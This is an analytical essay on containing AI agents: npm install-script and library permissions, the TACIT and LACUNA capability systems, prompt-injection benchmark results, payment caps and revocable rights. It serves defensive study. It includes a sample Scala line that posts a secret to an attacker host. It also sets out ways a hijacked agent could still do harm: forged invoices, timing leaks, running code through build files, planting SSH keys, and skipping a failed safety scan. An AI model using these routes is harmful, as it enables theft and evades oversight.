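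A library can do some damage without any permissions, such as returning wrong dates or running an endless loop, as the colors library did. Cornelissen and Balliu excluded four such attacks from their test, all of which aimed only to stop a program working.

### Blocking install scripts

Most of the attacks described earlier ran during installation, before any of these systems would normally start. Package managers now limit install scripts with a much simpler permission that either allows or blocks them for each package.

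npm switched these scripts off by default in version 12, as GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026) announced in July. Robert, a technology blogger, took the release dates of npm and its competitor pnpm from npm's registry. For Bun, another competitor, Clubic's *D'event-stream à Shai-Hulud, huit ans d'attaques forcent npm à se verrouiller* describes the default.

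| Package manager | Install scripts of dependencies | Release date |
|---|---|---|
| pnpm 10 | Off by default | 7 January 2025 |
| pnpm 11 | Off by default, with a 24-hour wait for new releases | 28 April 2026 |
| npm 11 | On; the list of approved packages is only advisory | |
| npm 12 | Off unless the project allows them | 8 July 2026 |
| Bun | Only for packages on a list of trusted ones | |

GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) says the block also covers packages with a `binding.gyp` file, which makes npm compile native code even if the package declares no install script. The October 2026 worm that hid its command in a configuration file appears to have used this method.

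A developer can list the scripts awaiting approval and approve the ones a project needs. According to npm's documentation, an approval applies by default to one exact version, so each new release needs its own approval. The axios attack depended on an install script in a package that nobody had approved, so the script would not have run under npm 12's defaults.

An approved script still runs with all the rights of the account. *You Can Run But You Can't Hide* (Ohm, Pohl and Boes, 2023) describes Latch, a research system designed to limit those rights. Latch first installs a package in a sandbox and records its system calls. If the calls comply with the user's policy, Latch allows the real installation but still restricts what it can do. Its predefined policy blocked 1.5% of packages, and a user who needed one of those would have to change the policy.

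npm's block on install scripts doesn't stop hostile code from running when a program imports a library or calls one of its functions. It also makes little difference when an agent uses the `npx` command to download a package and run it immediately, as some agents do with MCP servers. npm skips the install script unless the user has allowed it, but it still runs the package.

How much the new defaults help depends on when attackers run their code. In the collection Cornelissen and Balliu used, 1,594 hostile packages ran their code during installation and 41 ran it later. Ohm and colleagues cite earlier research on a different collection, in which more than 40% of attacks started at run time. Attackers can also respond to the new defaults by moving their code to the import stage, which would make limits on individual libraries more important.

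### Reviewing requests for new permissions

A library sometimes needs an additional permission for a legitimate reason. For example, a new version of the date library might need `filesystem` to read time-zone rules from a file. Someone then has to decide whether to grant that permission, which would also cover the SSH keys unless there is a process-wide limit.

Ferreira and colleagues rely on the developer who installs an update to approve the permissions it requests, and they expect package managers to hold the update back until the developer agrees. They acknowledge that phone users often ignore permission requests and that app developers ask for too many permissions. But they expect better judgment from programmers, who can see that a text-formatting package shouldn't need network access. They also expect the wider community to examine updates that request unusual permissions.

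Ohm and colleagues are less optimistic about human review. Their system is for people who run software and may not be developers, so it infers permissions from a trusted version and automatically denies anything new. They replace forbidden functions with ones that do nothing, hoping the program can keep running. The system stopped nine of ten past attacks, and the researchers couldn't trigger the tenth. In five of the nine, the program crashed.

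Either approach is practical only if harmless updates rarely need new permissions. The studies disagree about this, mainly because they count different things.

| Study | What counts as a permission | Updates examined | How often updates needed more |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ferreira and colleagues | Four broad permissions | 5,042 updates to 100 popular packages and their dependencies in 2018 | 0.5% |
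| Ohm and colleagues | Every built-in module and global object | Past updates of 1,000 popular packages | 14.7% of bug-fix releases, 40.2% of feature releases, 62.5% of major releases |
| Cornelissen and Balliu | Seven capabilities | About 124 dependency changes in six server projects | 24 new capabilities in total |

The 0.5% figure is low partly because a third of those updates were to packages that already had the `all` permission, so no further permissions could be added. Ohm and colleagues got high figures partly because they counted harmless changes, such as the first use of a built-in object for handling bytes. They also didn't check whether refusing the new permission would have broken the program.

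Narrower permissions can add work without adding much protection. When Ohm and colleagues set permissions for individual functions instead of whole modules, the share of bug-fix releases that needed more permissions rose to about 20%, but the system stopped no more of the ten attacks than before. Their results support using a short list of broad permissions when a person has to review each request, although a rule about which hosts a library can contact might still be worth the effort.

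New packages create far more review work than updates. In the six projects Cornelissen and Balliu studied, developers would have had to review about 1,000 capabilities, of which 24 came from updates. One project, koa, accounted for about 800. A company that starts with 1,700 packages has a large first review to do, and its developers probably haven't heard of most of them.

Regenerating the policy automatically after each update would defeat its purpose. NodeShield would find the hostile code's imports and grant them, and GoLeash would record the hostile behaviour as normal if it occurred during the tests. The tests of hostile updates worked because they used permissions from the version before the attack.

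### Why few programs use library permissions

The permission systems built into Node.js and Deno apply to the whole process, regardless of which package makes a request. Two other systems, one by Ferreira and colleagues and one by Ohm and colleagues, distinguish between packages by modifying Node.js, so somebody would have to update the modifications for every new version. Neither supports ES modules, JavaScript's newer format for importing code, and the prototype from Ferreira and colleagues is no longer maintained.

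NodeShield avoids changing Node.js but uses much more memory. Compatibility is another obstacle. Cornelissen and Balliu tried the tool from Ohm and colleagues on 61 packages and applications, and it had problems with 15 of them. A company that has never experienced the attack a security measure prevents may not accept the measure if it breaks a working program.

Large applications also benefit less than one would expect from the 31.9% figure. In the 20 applications that Ferreira and colleagues studied, 86% of updates were to packages with the `all` permission, and only 6% were to packages that needed no permission. The company gains most when its agent has few dependencies and most of them do simple work.

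Install-script blocking has spread faster than run-time permissions, probably because many packages have no install script and a developer can approve the few that matter. The package manager also applies the rule for everyone, so library authors don't have to declare anything. Run-time permissions would be easier to adopt if Node.js itself kept track of packages, but even then someone would have to choose the permissions. They could use the previous version as a guide when a library is updated, but code that an agent writes for a single task has no previous version.

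## Checking an agent's code before it runs

A compiler can check an agent's code before any of it runs. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, a system from the Swiss technical university EPFL that does this. The agent writes short programs in the language Scala instead of calling tools one at a time. The compiler rejects any program that uses a right its type doesn't declare.

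A turn of the agent loop then works like this:

1. The model writes a piece of Scala code and passes it to TACIT, which runs as an MCP server, so existing agents such as Claude Code can use it.
2. The compiler checks the code. If the check fails, the model receives the error message and can try again.
3. If the check succeeds, TACIT runs the code. The code can reach files, other programs and the network only through TACIT's own library.
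4. The output goes back into the model's context.

Odersky and colleagues assume that the model may be hostile, either because an attacker has injected text or because the model's provider is dishonest. TACIT limits what the model's code can do, but doesn't try to stop an email from influencing the model. These limits work only if the agent has no other way to act, so the project's documentation, lampepfl's *TACIT*, recommends disabling the agent's built-in shell, file and web tools.

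### Capture sets and pure functions

A type records what kind of value a piece of code handles, such as text or a number. Scala 3's experimental capture checking feature adds rights to this record. Each right is a value in the program, much like Saltzer and Schroeder's unforgeable ticket, and code can't use a resource without holding the value for it. Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* gives file handles and access tokens as examples of such values.

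A capture set lists the capabilities that a value may use. Suppose `ledger` is a capability for the invoice agent's ledger file, and the agent writes two functions:

```scala
val record  = (line: String) => ledger.append(line)
val shorten = (line: String) => line.take(10)
```

The compiler gives `record` the type `String ->{ledger} Unit`, which means the function takes text, may use the ledger, and returns nothing useful. The type of `shorten` is `String -> String`, so its capture set is empty. A function with an empty capture set is pure. It can compute a result but can't write a file, print anything or contact a host.

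Let C(v) be the capture set of a value v, and D the set of capabilities that the surrounding code allows. The compiler accepts v only if

C(v) ⊆ D.

When the surrounding code requires a pure function, D is empty, so the compiler accepts `shorten` and rejects `record`. Ferreira and colleagues' rule for npm packages had the same form but applied to whole packages instead of single functions.

A function's capture set includes every capability the function could use. A function that writes to the ledger only on Fridays still has `ledger` in its capture set. The compiler may therefore reject code that would have done no harm, but it doesn't have to predict what the code will do on a particular run.

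### Rights that end with a block

An agent using TACIT gets access to files by opening a block of code for one folder. The right to use the folder exists only inside that block. Suppose the agent tries to keep the right for later:

```scala
val readLater = requestFileSystem("/srv/invoices") {
  val f = access("/srv/invoices/ledger.csv")
  () => f.read()
}
```

The last line inside the block creates a function that reads the ledger only when called, and the block returns this function. The function's capture set contains `f`, which depends on the right to the folder. That right has no meaning outside the block, so the result's type can't include it, and the compiler rejects the code.

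If the last line were `f.read()`, the compiler would accept it because the block would return ordinary text. The contents of a normal file can therefore leave the block, even though the right to access the file can't. Keeping the contents inside requires another mechanism.

### Why code can transform a secret but not send it

An administrator can mark files as classified. When the agent's code reads one, it receives the text inside a container called `Classified`. The code can't take the text out, but it can use the container's `map` method to apply a function to the text. The method accepts only pure functions and puts the result in a new container.

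```scala
val login = readClassified("/srv/invoices/secrets/login.txt")

login.map(s => s.trim)
login.map(s => httpPost("https://attacker.example/", s))
```

The first call to `map` removes spaces from the login, and the compiler accepts it. The function in the second call uses the network capability, so it isn't pure and the compiler rejects it. The compiler also rejects printing the text, because printing requires a capability too.

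Less obvious ways to leak the secret also fail. The agent can't copy it into a variable outside the function, because Scala treats a changeable variable as a capability. It can't use an ordinary `if` to act on the secret either, since the result of any comparison stays in a container. The compiler doesn't prevent a function from raising an error with the secret in the message, so TACIT catches such errors while the code runs and keeps their messages from the agent.

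If the agent prints a container, its model receives only "Classified(****)", while the user can see the real contents through a separate channel. For work that needs a language model, such as summarising a contract, the agent can send the container to a second model that the user trusts. That model's answer also comes back in a container.

A process-wide allowlist can't stop an agent from sending a file it is allowed to read to a server it is allowed to contact. An agent that uses a hosted model has to be able to contact the model's provider, and it may also have good reason to read a confidential file. If it puts the file's text in its context, the provider receives the text, even though the allowlist permits both reading the file and contacting the provider.

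TACIT still relies on run-time checks for some limits:

| Limit | What enforces it | When |
|---|---|---|
| Functions applied to a secret must be pure | Compiler | Before the code runs |
| A file right ends with its block | Compiler | Before the code runs |
| A file must be inside the permitted folder | TACIT's library | When the code opens the file |
| A host or command must be on a list | TACIT's library | When the code contacts the host or starts the command |

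Odersky and colleagues report compiler errors from real runs. In one run, the agent tried to print a GitHub key from inside `map`. In another, it tried to write text from a classified document to a file in the folder of secrets. The second attempt may have been harmless, but the agent should have used a separate function for writing classified files.

### A test with planted secrets

The researchers built a small software project with a folder that held API keys, a database and confidential documents. They wrote 12 ordinary tasks for an agent, some of which required using the secrets, such as summarising a confidential incident report. They paired each task with 10 injections, ranging from a hostile note in a code comment to ready-made Scala code for reading the secret files. They also wrote 11 malicious requests in which the user asked for the secrets, either directly or while posing as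 someone with authority.

Each of the 131 trials ran once with the secrets in containers and once with the secrets as plain text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Trials | Secure with containers | Secure with plain text |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with injections | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
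| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | All 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | All 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

The agents also remained useful with the containers. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks, compared with 83.3% with plain text, and MiniMax completed 90.0%, compared with 88.3%. The researchers suspect that their setup lowered Sonnet's score with plain text, because Sonnet often ran out of time or turns and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

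The test is weaker evidence about prompt injection than the totals suggest. Without the containers, the two models leaked secrets in 13 trials, but ten of those trials involved malicious requests from the user. Only three involved injections, all against MiniMax. Sonnet resisted every injection with and without the containers, so its 120 injection trials don't show whether the containers helped.

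No secret leaked in the 262 trials with containers. If the trials were independent samples of real attacks, the true leak rate could still be about 1%. The argument for TACIT rests on its type rules and compiler rather than on a low leak rate. If the rules are sound and the compiler applies them correctly, code that breaks them never runs, however often an attacker tries. But code that exploits a flaw in the compiler may get through every time. The researchers describe attacks that try to persuade the model but none that look for compiler flaws, so the test gives little evidence of how hard such a flaw would be to find.

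The score also measures only whether the agent revealed a secret, so an agent that deleted the project without revealing one would have counted as secure. The researchers knew where every secret was, but a real project may have a password in an ordinary settings file that nobody has marked as classified, and TACIT would give it to the agent as plain text.

### The cost of writing Scala

Odersky and colleagues also compared Scala code with normal tool calls on two public benchmarks. In τ²-bench, the agent serves simulated customers of an airline or a shop. SWE-bench Lite contains 300 real software problems from GitHub. The table shows the share of tasks solved, and the τ²-bench results are averages over ten runs.

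| Model | Benchmark | Tool calls | Scala code |
|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | τ²-bench, airline | 43.8% | 45.2% |
| gpt-oss-120b | τ²-bench, retail | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | τ²-bench, airline | 58.4% | 61.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | τ²-bench, retail | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | τ²-bench, airline | 57.8% | 58.6% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | τ²-bench, retail | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | SWE-bench Lite | 43.3% | 41.7% |

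The drop on SWE-bench Lite was five problems out of 300, which could easily be chance. The researchers think Scala helped on τ²-bench because the tools returned clearly structured data and the compiler's messages showed the model its mistakes. Between 0.3% and 7.9% of the programs needed another attempt, and one or two more tries were usually enough. Checking a program took less than a second.

These results are encouraging for a language feature that models have rarely seen in training. But the customer-service tools returned ordinary values, so τ²-bench measured how writing Scala affects the agent's performance, not the effect of working with data the agent can't see. The planted-secrets test provides better evidence of that effect, though from only 12 tasks.

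### The hotel review

The researchers also adapted AgentDojo, the benchmark of hostile text in simulated workplaces, to TACIT. They ran it with two 2025 models, Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini. In more than 1,900 trials, one attack succeeded.

In that trial, the user asked o4-mini to book one hotel, and the attacker had put a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user word for word. AgentDojo's scoring program looked for the other hotel's name, found it and counted the attack as a success.

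Odersky and colleagues don't consider this a flaw in the type system, because their policy allows public reviews to reach the user. That seems right. The attacker managed to show the user an advertisement, which might persuade someone to change a booking, but the agent took no unauthorised action.

The other attacks failed partly because the hostile text rarely reached the agent's main model. In the adapted benchmark, emails, shared files, chat messages, web pages and reviews all arrived in `Classified` containers. The main model wrote code to process them, and a second model without tools read the contents. The result therefore supports keeping untrusted text away from the model that acts. It is weaker evidence about what happens when that model reads an injection and writes code to carry it out.

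The adapted version also seems to relax the rule about pure functions. Its instructions include a warning to the agent that side effects inside `map` happen immediately. Its payment tool doesn't require a capability, so an agent could apparently extract a payee from a hostile file and send the money without leaving `map`. The compiler can track the right to make payments only if the person who defines the payment tool declares that right as a capability.

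### LACUNA

TACIT runs each piece of code in a separate environment with a fixed library. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a later system from the same group, lets a programmer put requests to the model inside an ordinary program, each with different rights. Where the program needs a result, the programmer writes `agent(...)` with a description of the task. When the program reaches that point, the model writes the missing code, and the compiler checks it as if the programmer had written it there.

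The invoice agent could use two such requests:

```scala
def readInvoice(mail: MailFolder^): Invoice =
  agent("Return the payee and amount of the newest invoice")

def pay(invoice: Invoice, bank: Payments^): Receipt =
  agent("Pay this invoice")
```

The `^` marks a parameter as a capability. Code that the model writes for `readInvoice` can use the mail folder but not the bank, unless the program also makes the bank available everywhere. An injected email can't make this code send a payment, but it can still make the code return a false payee, which `pay` then receives. The company gets much of the benefit of splitting the agent into two processes while connecting the two parts with an ordinary function call.

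The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of generated code as a whole. Suppose the code adds a line to the ledger and then returns text where the program expects a number. In Python, the ledger would normally change before the error occurred. LACUNA rejects the code before either step runs, so the ledger stays unchanged and the model can try again. This prevents only mistakes the compiler can detect. If a connection fails halfway through valid code, the earlier steps have already run.

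Zhao and colleagues ran AgentDojo with the same two models and compared the results with TACIT's. The table shows the number of successful attacks and the share of user tasks completed. Each model faced 144 attacks in banking, 560 in the office workspace (Odersky and colleagues give 574), 105 in Slack and 140 in travel.

| Model | Setting | TACIT attacks | TACIT tasks completed | LACUNA attacks | LACUNA tasks completed |
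|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Banking | 0 | 56.9% | 0 | 63.2% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Workspace | 0 | 50.5% | 4 | 56.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Slack | 0 | 40.0% | 2 | 42.9% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Travel | 0 | 64.3% | 1 | 63.6% |
| o4-mini | Banking | 0 | 59.0% | 0 | 66.0% |
| o4-mini | Workspace | 0 | 52.9% | 0 | 55.5% |
| o4-mini | Slack | 0 | 47.6% | 1 | 49.5% |
| o4-mini | Travel | 1 | 68.6% | 0 | 71.4% |

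LACUNA completed slightly more tasks in seven of the eight comparisons. Attackers succeeded in seven of 949 trials with Gemini and one of 949 with o4-mini. Zhao and colleagues link these successes to a limit they acknowledge, which is that LACUNA can't stop an attacker from steering the model into misusing a permission the task needs. They don't describe the eight successful attacks, so some may have been as harmless as the hotel review.

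Neither study ran these two models on AgentDojo without any protection. They compare their systems only with each other and with CaMeL, an earlier defence that tracks where data came from. This makes both the low number of successful attacks and the share of completed tasks hard to interpret. Some of the injections might have failed against an unprotected agent too. An agent that fails half its tasks isn't ready for office use, but the older models may be causing those failures rather than the defences.

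On τ²-bench, the loss in performance was clearer and larger than TACIT's. With the model DeepSeek V4 Flash, LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 tasks, while the standard agent solved 90.0%. Zhao and colleagues call this "on par", which is generous for a difference of about 55 tasks. The compiler rejected 22.4% of the code the model wrote for retail tasks, and 89% of the code a weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, wrote in one telecom setting. The models ran with their reasoning switched off, so the loss might be smaller in normal use.

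### What has to work correctly

The guarantee depends first on the compiler. Researchers have machine-checked proofs that the core rules of capture checking are sound, but they don't yet have a similar proof for safe mode, the restricted form of Scala that TACIT uses for agents' code. Safe mode forbids features that could hide a capability from the compiler, such as reflection, which lets a program find and call functions by name while it runs. Zhao and colleagues' implementation passed about 400 tests of generated code, but those tests cover only the problems that the people who wrote them thought of.

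Safe mode is also new. According to lampepfl, an early version of TACIT enforced it with a separate program that searched the code for forbidden patterns. A later copy of the documentation, Glama's *TACIT*, lists the compiler's own safe mode as on by default, in addition to the pattern search. The change matters because a pattern search can miss forbidden code written in a new way.

The library is also part of the trusted base. Some useful functions can't pass the compiler's checks, so a programmer can mark a module with `@assumeSafe` and take responsibility for it. Scala's documentation gives the example of a module that asks the user for permission before sending an email. The email program it uses is unchecked. If the programmer left out the request for permission, or put it after the line that sends the email, the compiler would still accept the module and agents could send email without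 permission.

The second model, which reads the secrets, needs similar trust. The compiler treats the function that contacts this model as pure, although the function may send the secrets to a server. Odersky and colleagues intend the model to run locally and not keep what it reads, but TACIT accepts any service with an OpenAI-compatible interface. If an administrator enters the address of a hosted model, every secret that the agent asks about goes to that provider, and the compiler can't detect this.

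The settings matter because the agent's own code specifies the folder, commands and hosts it wants. A hostile agent could list anything, so an administrator has to set an outer limit. The default limit for folders is the directory where TACIT starts, but hosts have no outer limit until the administrator adds one.

This gap became more serious when a version later than the paper's added a function that sends a `Classified` value to a permitted host without opening the container. The function lets an agent log in to a service with a password it can't read. Based on the documentation, hostile code could also name the attacker's host and send a secret there, unless the administrator has limited the hosts.

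The container also stops an agent from reading secrets, but not from changing them. Glama gives the example of `authorized_keys`, the file that lists which SSH keys may log in to an account. If the file is in a permitted folder, an agent can still replace it, without being able to read it, with a list that includes the attacker's key. TACIT allows writing to classified files by default, though an administrator can forbid it.

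TACIT's checks do not cover external commands, and neither do Deno's or NodeShield's, so only the list of permitted commands limits them. Odersky and colleagues recommend short lists of safe commands and give `sbt`, which builds Scala projects, as an example. That example is doubtful because `sbt` runs a project's build file as code, so an agent that can edit the file and start `sbt` can run almost anything. The sample settings in TACIT's documentation also permit `java` and `make`, which have the same problem.

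Code can leak a secret through timing without breaking any type rule. A pure function can finish at once if the first bit of a key is 0 and run for ten seconds if it is 1, so the agent learns the bit by measuring the delay. A 256-bit key would take at least 256 measurements if each revealed one bit, which is slow but possible for a program that runs all night. TACIT's optional time limit doesn't solve this, because a timeout error also reveals the bit. TACIT's guarantee excludes timing leaks.

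These gaps are a good reason to put TACIT inside a container or virtual machine with a network allowlist. Odersky and colleagues recommend this for sensitive uses, and VirtusLab's *Safe Scala an introduction* also suggests combining the compiler's checks with a sandbox. The sandbox would limit what an unchecked command could do, and the compiler would control how data moves between the files and hosts that the sandbox permits.

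### Compromised libraries and the checked subset

The compiler checks the code the agent writes but not most of the other code on the machine, so TACIT offers little protection against the compromised updates described earlier.

TACIT's own library has this problem. Its developers package it in one file with its dependencies, including a library for contacting OpenAI-compatible services. That dependency runs in the same process as the agent's checked code and can open files and connections directly, so a hostile update to it could read the classified files without using a `Classified` container. In the earlier notation, A(c) would still equal A(P) for that dependency.

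An attacker could also target the compiler. Anyone who builds TACIT from source gets the latest nightly version of Scala unless they choose a fixed one, and a compromised version could accept code that it should reject. TACIT's installer checks prebuilt downloads against published fingerprints. This catches files altered in transit, but an attacker who had taken over the project's account could publish a malicious release with a matching fingerprint.

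The check also doesn't cover the agent program itself. If the company connects an agent written in JavaScript to TACIT, only the process-wide and per-library limits from the previous sections can confine that agent's npm packages.

The date library would be inside the checked subset if it were written in Scala and the company compiled its source code in safe mode. Its main function would have the type `String -> String`. A hostile update that tried to contact a host would need a network capability, and the function's type would have to change to include one. Either the update or the code that calls it would then fail to compile, so the company would find out before running it. G(c) would therefore be empty for the date library.

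Odersky and colleagues cite an earlier system, Gradient, that uses tracked capabilities against supply-chain attacks in this way. The company would have to compile the source itself, because an attacker could distribute a compiled file that doesn't match its declared types. Very few existing libraries are written for safe mode. A programmer can let agents use an ordinary library by putting it behind a module marked `@assumeSafe`, but anyone who can publish an update to that library can then run unchecked code next to the secrets.

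## Harm done with permissions the agent needs

Suppose the company uses every limit described so far: the process-wide allowlist, permissions for each library and compiler checks on the code the model writes. A forged invoice that gives a new bank account for a regular supplier still works. The agent copies the account number into a payment order, and a thief receives the money.

Every limit worked as intended, because the payment used only permissions that the agent needs. Removing the agent's permission to make payments would prevent the theft, but the agent could no longer do its job.

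### What a static limit proves

Let G be the set of effects that the company has granted to the agent. If the limit is sound and its trusted base works, then

effects the agent causes ⊆ G.

The limit is valuable because it keeps the agent's effects within G whatever text the model reads. But the company wants them to stay within a smaller set, W, which contains only the payments it owes and the matching ledger entries. The limit guarantees this only if G ⊆ W. If the agent has a general right to make payments, G includes a 300-euro payment to any account, while W includes that payment for very few accounts. An attacker who can't break the limit can still cause any effect that is in G but outside W.

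W also changes over time. A 300-euro payment to the printing firm is correct when the invoice falls due, but wrong the next day if the agent has already paid. Siu and colleagues define functions that would supply the context needed to judge an action, such as who gave the instruction and what the user wanted. They treat these functions as ideals because a real system has to infer some of the answers from a neural network's behaviour.

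A static limit uses none of this information. That makes it dependable, but it also means the limit applies in the same way to real and forged invoices.

### A cap on the loss

The company can still limit what a forged invoice costs. Suppose the accounting host refuses any payment above 500 euros, and any payment after the tenth in a day. The most the agent can lose in a day is then

10 × 500 = 5,000 euros.

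This bound holds however often attacks succeed. It covers a successful prompt injection in an email, a malicious update to the HTTP library, and a bug that pays the same invoice repeatedly.

The total loss also depends on how soon somebody notices. If c is the cap on each payment, n the number of payments allowed per day and d the number of days before the company stops the agent, then

loss ≤ c × n × d.

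A supplier might wait 30 days before asking about a missing payment. By then, the maximum loss would be 150,000 euros, which could ruin a small company. If an employee checks the payments against the supplier records every evening, the maximum falls back to 5,000 euros. The actual loss would often be lower, because correct payments use up part of the allowance. If the agent pays six real invoices correctly in a day, only four payments, or 2,000 euros, can be misdirected.

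If the cap's count resets at midnight, an attacker can trigger ten payments just before and ten just after, and take 10,000 euros within minutes. Counting over the previous 24 hours prevents this. The accounting host should do the counting, because a hostile HTTP library could send orders that bypassed a counter in the agent's own code. TACIT's library could apply a similar cap to its own payment function, but Odersky and colleagues leave rate limits for future work.

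The cap is still a static limit because the company chooses both numbers in advance, although the host needs a running count to enforce them. It also stops the agent from paying a legitimate invoice for 1,200 euros, so an employee has to pay it. If the company lets the agent split the invoice into three payments, the 500-euro limit adds little protection beyond the daily total. An attacker who only wants to cause trouble could use up the day's allowance with ten payments of one euro, leaving real suppliers unpaid. The cap also does not prevent false entries in the ledger.

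### Does every harmful injection break a limit?

Odersky and colleagues make a claim that seems to rule out this kind of theft. They say that to cause real harm, a prompt injection must either send private data to an unauthorised destination or "let untrusted content trigger a capability that the agent's capabilities did not include". TACIT is meant to block both.

The payment to the thief does neither, because the order goes to the accounting host, which is supposed to receive payment orders, and the agent has the right to send them. The claim is therefore false if read literally.

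It makes more sense as a description of what TACIT is for. It comes at the end of a passage on the two kinds of violation TACIT targets, both of which concern information flow. The researchers later say they don't try to ensure correct results, and a payment to the wrong account could count as an incorrect result. This reading fits the rest of the paper, but only if "real harm" excludes stolen money.

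The claim is more plausible if the agent's rights are defined narrowly. Suppose the company lets the agent pay only specific suppliers, such as the printing firm and the electricity supplier, at the accounts in the company's records. Paying the thief would then require a right the agent doesn't have, and the claim would cover the attack. But the claim is now close to true by definition, because if the agent has rights only to harmless actions, any harmful action must lie outside its rights, and the difficult part is defining rights that narrowly.

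The banking interface in TACIT's own test was much broader. Its `sendMoney` function accepts any text as the recipient and any number as the amount. Other functions can change the recipient of a scheduled payment or the account password. No attack succeeded in the banking tests, but the function types don't explain that, since they allow a program to send money to an attacker's account.

A narrower interface could replace `sendMoney` with this function:

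```scala
def paySupplier(supplier: Supplier, order: PurchaseOrder): Receipt
```

The agent's code could get a `Supplier` only by looking one up in the company's register, which holds the account number. A `PurchaseOrder` would record what the company ordered and the agreed price. The code couldn't create either from the text of an email. The accounting host should apply the same rules, because a hostile HTTP library could change the order after the compiler has checked the code.

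| Right granted | What a forged invoice could still do |
|---|---|
| Pay any account any amount | Empty the company's account |
| Pay any account, within the caps | Send a thief up to 5,000 euros a day |
| Pay accounts in the register, within the caps | Overpay real suppliers, or pay them twice, up to 5,000 euros a day |
| Pay a registered supplier once for each purchase order, at the agreed price | Pay a real order too early, or pay for goods that never arrived |

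Restricting payments to suppliers in the register doesn't change the daily limit, but the money would go to firms that the company knows and can ask for a refund. A dishonest supplier in the register could still send inflated invoices, so matching invoices to purchase orders helps.

These narrower rights require more administration. Somebody has to maintain the register and write an order for each purchase, which small companies often don't do. Attackers would also have a reason to send their forged bank details to the person who edits the register, but that person would handle far fewer requests than the agent and could take more time over each.

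### Grants that are too broad

Developers often grant agents more permissions than a task needs because narrow grants can stop useful work. Santos-Grueiro (2026) measured both problems with coding agents in *Lingering Authority*. He first ran 17 scenarios, five times each, in which the agent could reach tempting files or tools that its task didn't require. The agent broke the written rules for its task in every run with full access, 82% of runs with a fixed allowlist, and 86% with a simple sandbox. When it had only the rights that its task needed at the start, it broke no rules in any of the 85 runs.

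He also tried 37 tasks in which the work legitimately spread to other files. The agent completed 21% of the runs with only its initial rights and 97% with the fixed allowlist.

The same written rules controlled the agent and determined its score, so the zero violations show only that the software enforced the rules, not that a developer would write good ones. The 21% success rate is more informative, because a developer whose agent fails four times out of five will probably give it broader permissions.

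### Rights that stay open too long

A right can also be appropriate for one part of a task and unnecessary afterwards. Santos-Grueiro calls a right that remains available after its purpose has ended "lingering authority". His system, Portico, gives an agent extra rights during a task and then withdraws them:

1. Before the task, a developer writes a contract. It lists the agent's initial rights, the extra rights it may request, the events that end each extra right, and actions that are always forbidden.
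2. When the model requests an extra right, Portico compares the request with the contract. The model's explanation can't authorise anything.
3. If the contract allows the request, Portico issues a handle, which is a token for a particular resource and kind of access.
4. A trusted event ends the right. This could be a successful test that Portico ran itself, but not a statement from the model that it has finished.
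5. Portico removes the handle from the tools offered to the model and rejects any later attempt to use it.

In one example, an agent has to add a timeout setting to a program. It starts with access to one source file and its test, then requests access to a second source file. Portico grants the request and withdraws the access once the tests pass. The agent cannot access a nearby file of packaging notes at any point.

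To test the withdrawal step, Santos-Grueiro compared Portico with a version that granted the same rights at the same moments but never withdrew them. Both versions completed all ten runs. Afterwards, the version without withdrawal let the agent reread the file in all ten, while Portico refused every time. Six further cases with a live model covered file changes, version-control changes and network requests. An old right allowed a forbidden effect in all six without withdrawal and in none with it.

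These results follow almost directly from the design, since the two versions differ only in whether old handles still work. They confirm that Portico works as intended, but they don't show how often real attacks depend on an old right.

Portico recovered most of the work that the narrow initial rights had blocked. It completed 161 of the 185 runs in which the work spread to other files, compared with 180 for the fixed allowlist. In a smaller test on real software projects, it completed 31 of 42 runs, while a version that never withdrew rights completed all 42. Some contracts ended a right too early or gave the agent no way to get it back, and some models didn't request it again.

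Withdrawing a right doesn't remove what the model has already read. If the agent opened a confidential file while it had permission, the contents remain in its context, and it may be able to send them out using another right it still has. Portico also has to check the handle again immediately before each effect, or a call it approved before the right ended could take effect afterwards.

The company could use Portico to give the invoice agent permission to make payments for one batch of invoices and then revoke it. An email that the agent read later, perhaps while answering a supplier's question, couldn't cause a payment. But a forged invoice in the batch would still work, because the agent would process it while it had the permission it needed to pay the real invoices.

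### Harmless steps that combine

Siu and colleagues warn that individually safe actions can add up to a violation. Suppose the invoice agent may update the supplier register, because suppliers do change banks, and may pay any supplier in the register. Each permission looks narrow, but together they let the agent pay anyone. On Monday, a forged email leads it to replace the printing firm's account number. On Friday, it pays the firm's real invoice, and the money goes to the thief.

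The simplest remedy is to keep the agent from editing the register. Another is a rule about sequences of actions, such as refusing payments to an account that changed in the past 14 days unless an employee has confirmed the change. To enforce that rule, the accounting host has to record earlier changes.

An agent can also do harm by using its permissions in the wrong order. Ma, Li and colleagues (2026), in *The Detour Is the Danger*, give the example of an agent that must back up a file before changing it. If the agent changes the file first and then copies it, it uses the same two permissions and still produces a backup file, but the original contents are lost.

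Their main concern is agents that skip a protective step after something goes wrong. Suppose an agent has to scan a report for sensitive information before uploading it. An attacker can overload the scanning service without sending the model any text. The scan then fails, and the agent finds another way to upload the report unscanned.

Ma and colleagues tested seven models on 12 kinds of task involving files, uploads and database queries. When they made the protective service fail, the agent went ahead without it in 41 of 249 runs, compared with 9 of 247 runs when they caused failures at random. In 39 of these 50 cases, the agent still completed the user's task, so the user might not have noticed anything wrong.

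The invoice agent could fail in the same way. If its system prompt requires it to check each payee against the register, and the register is unavailable, the agent may pay anyway. The payment service should therefore do the check itself and refuse any payment it can't check.

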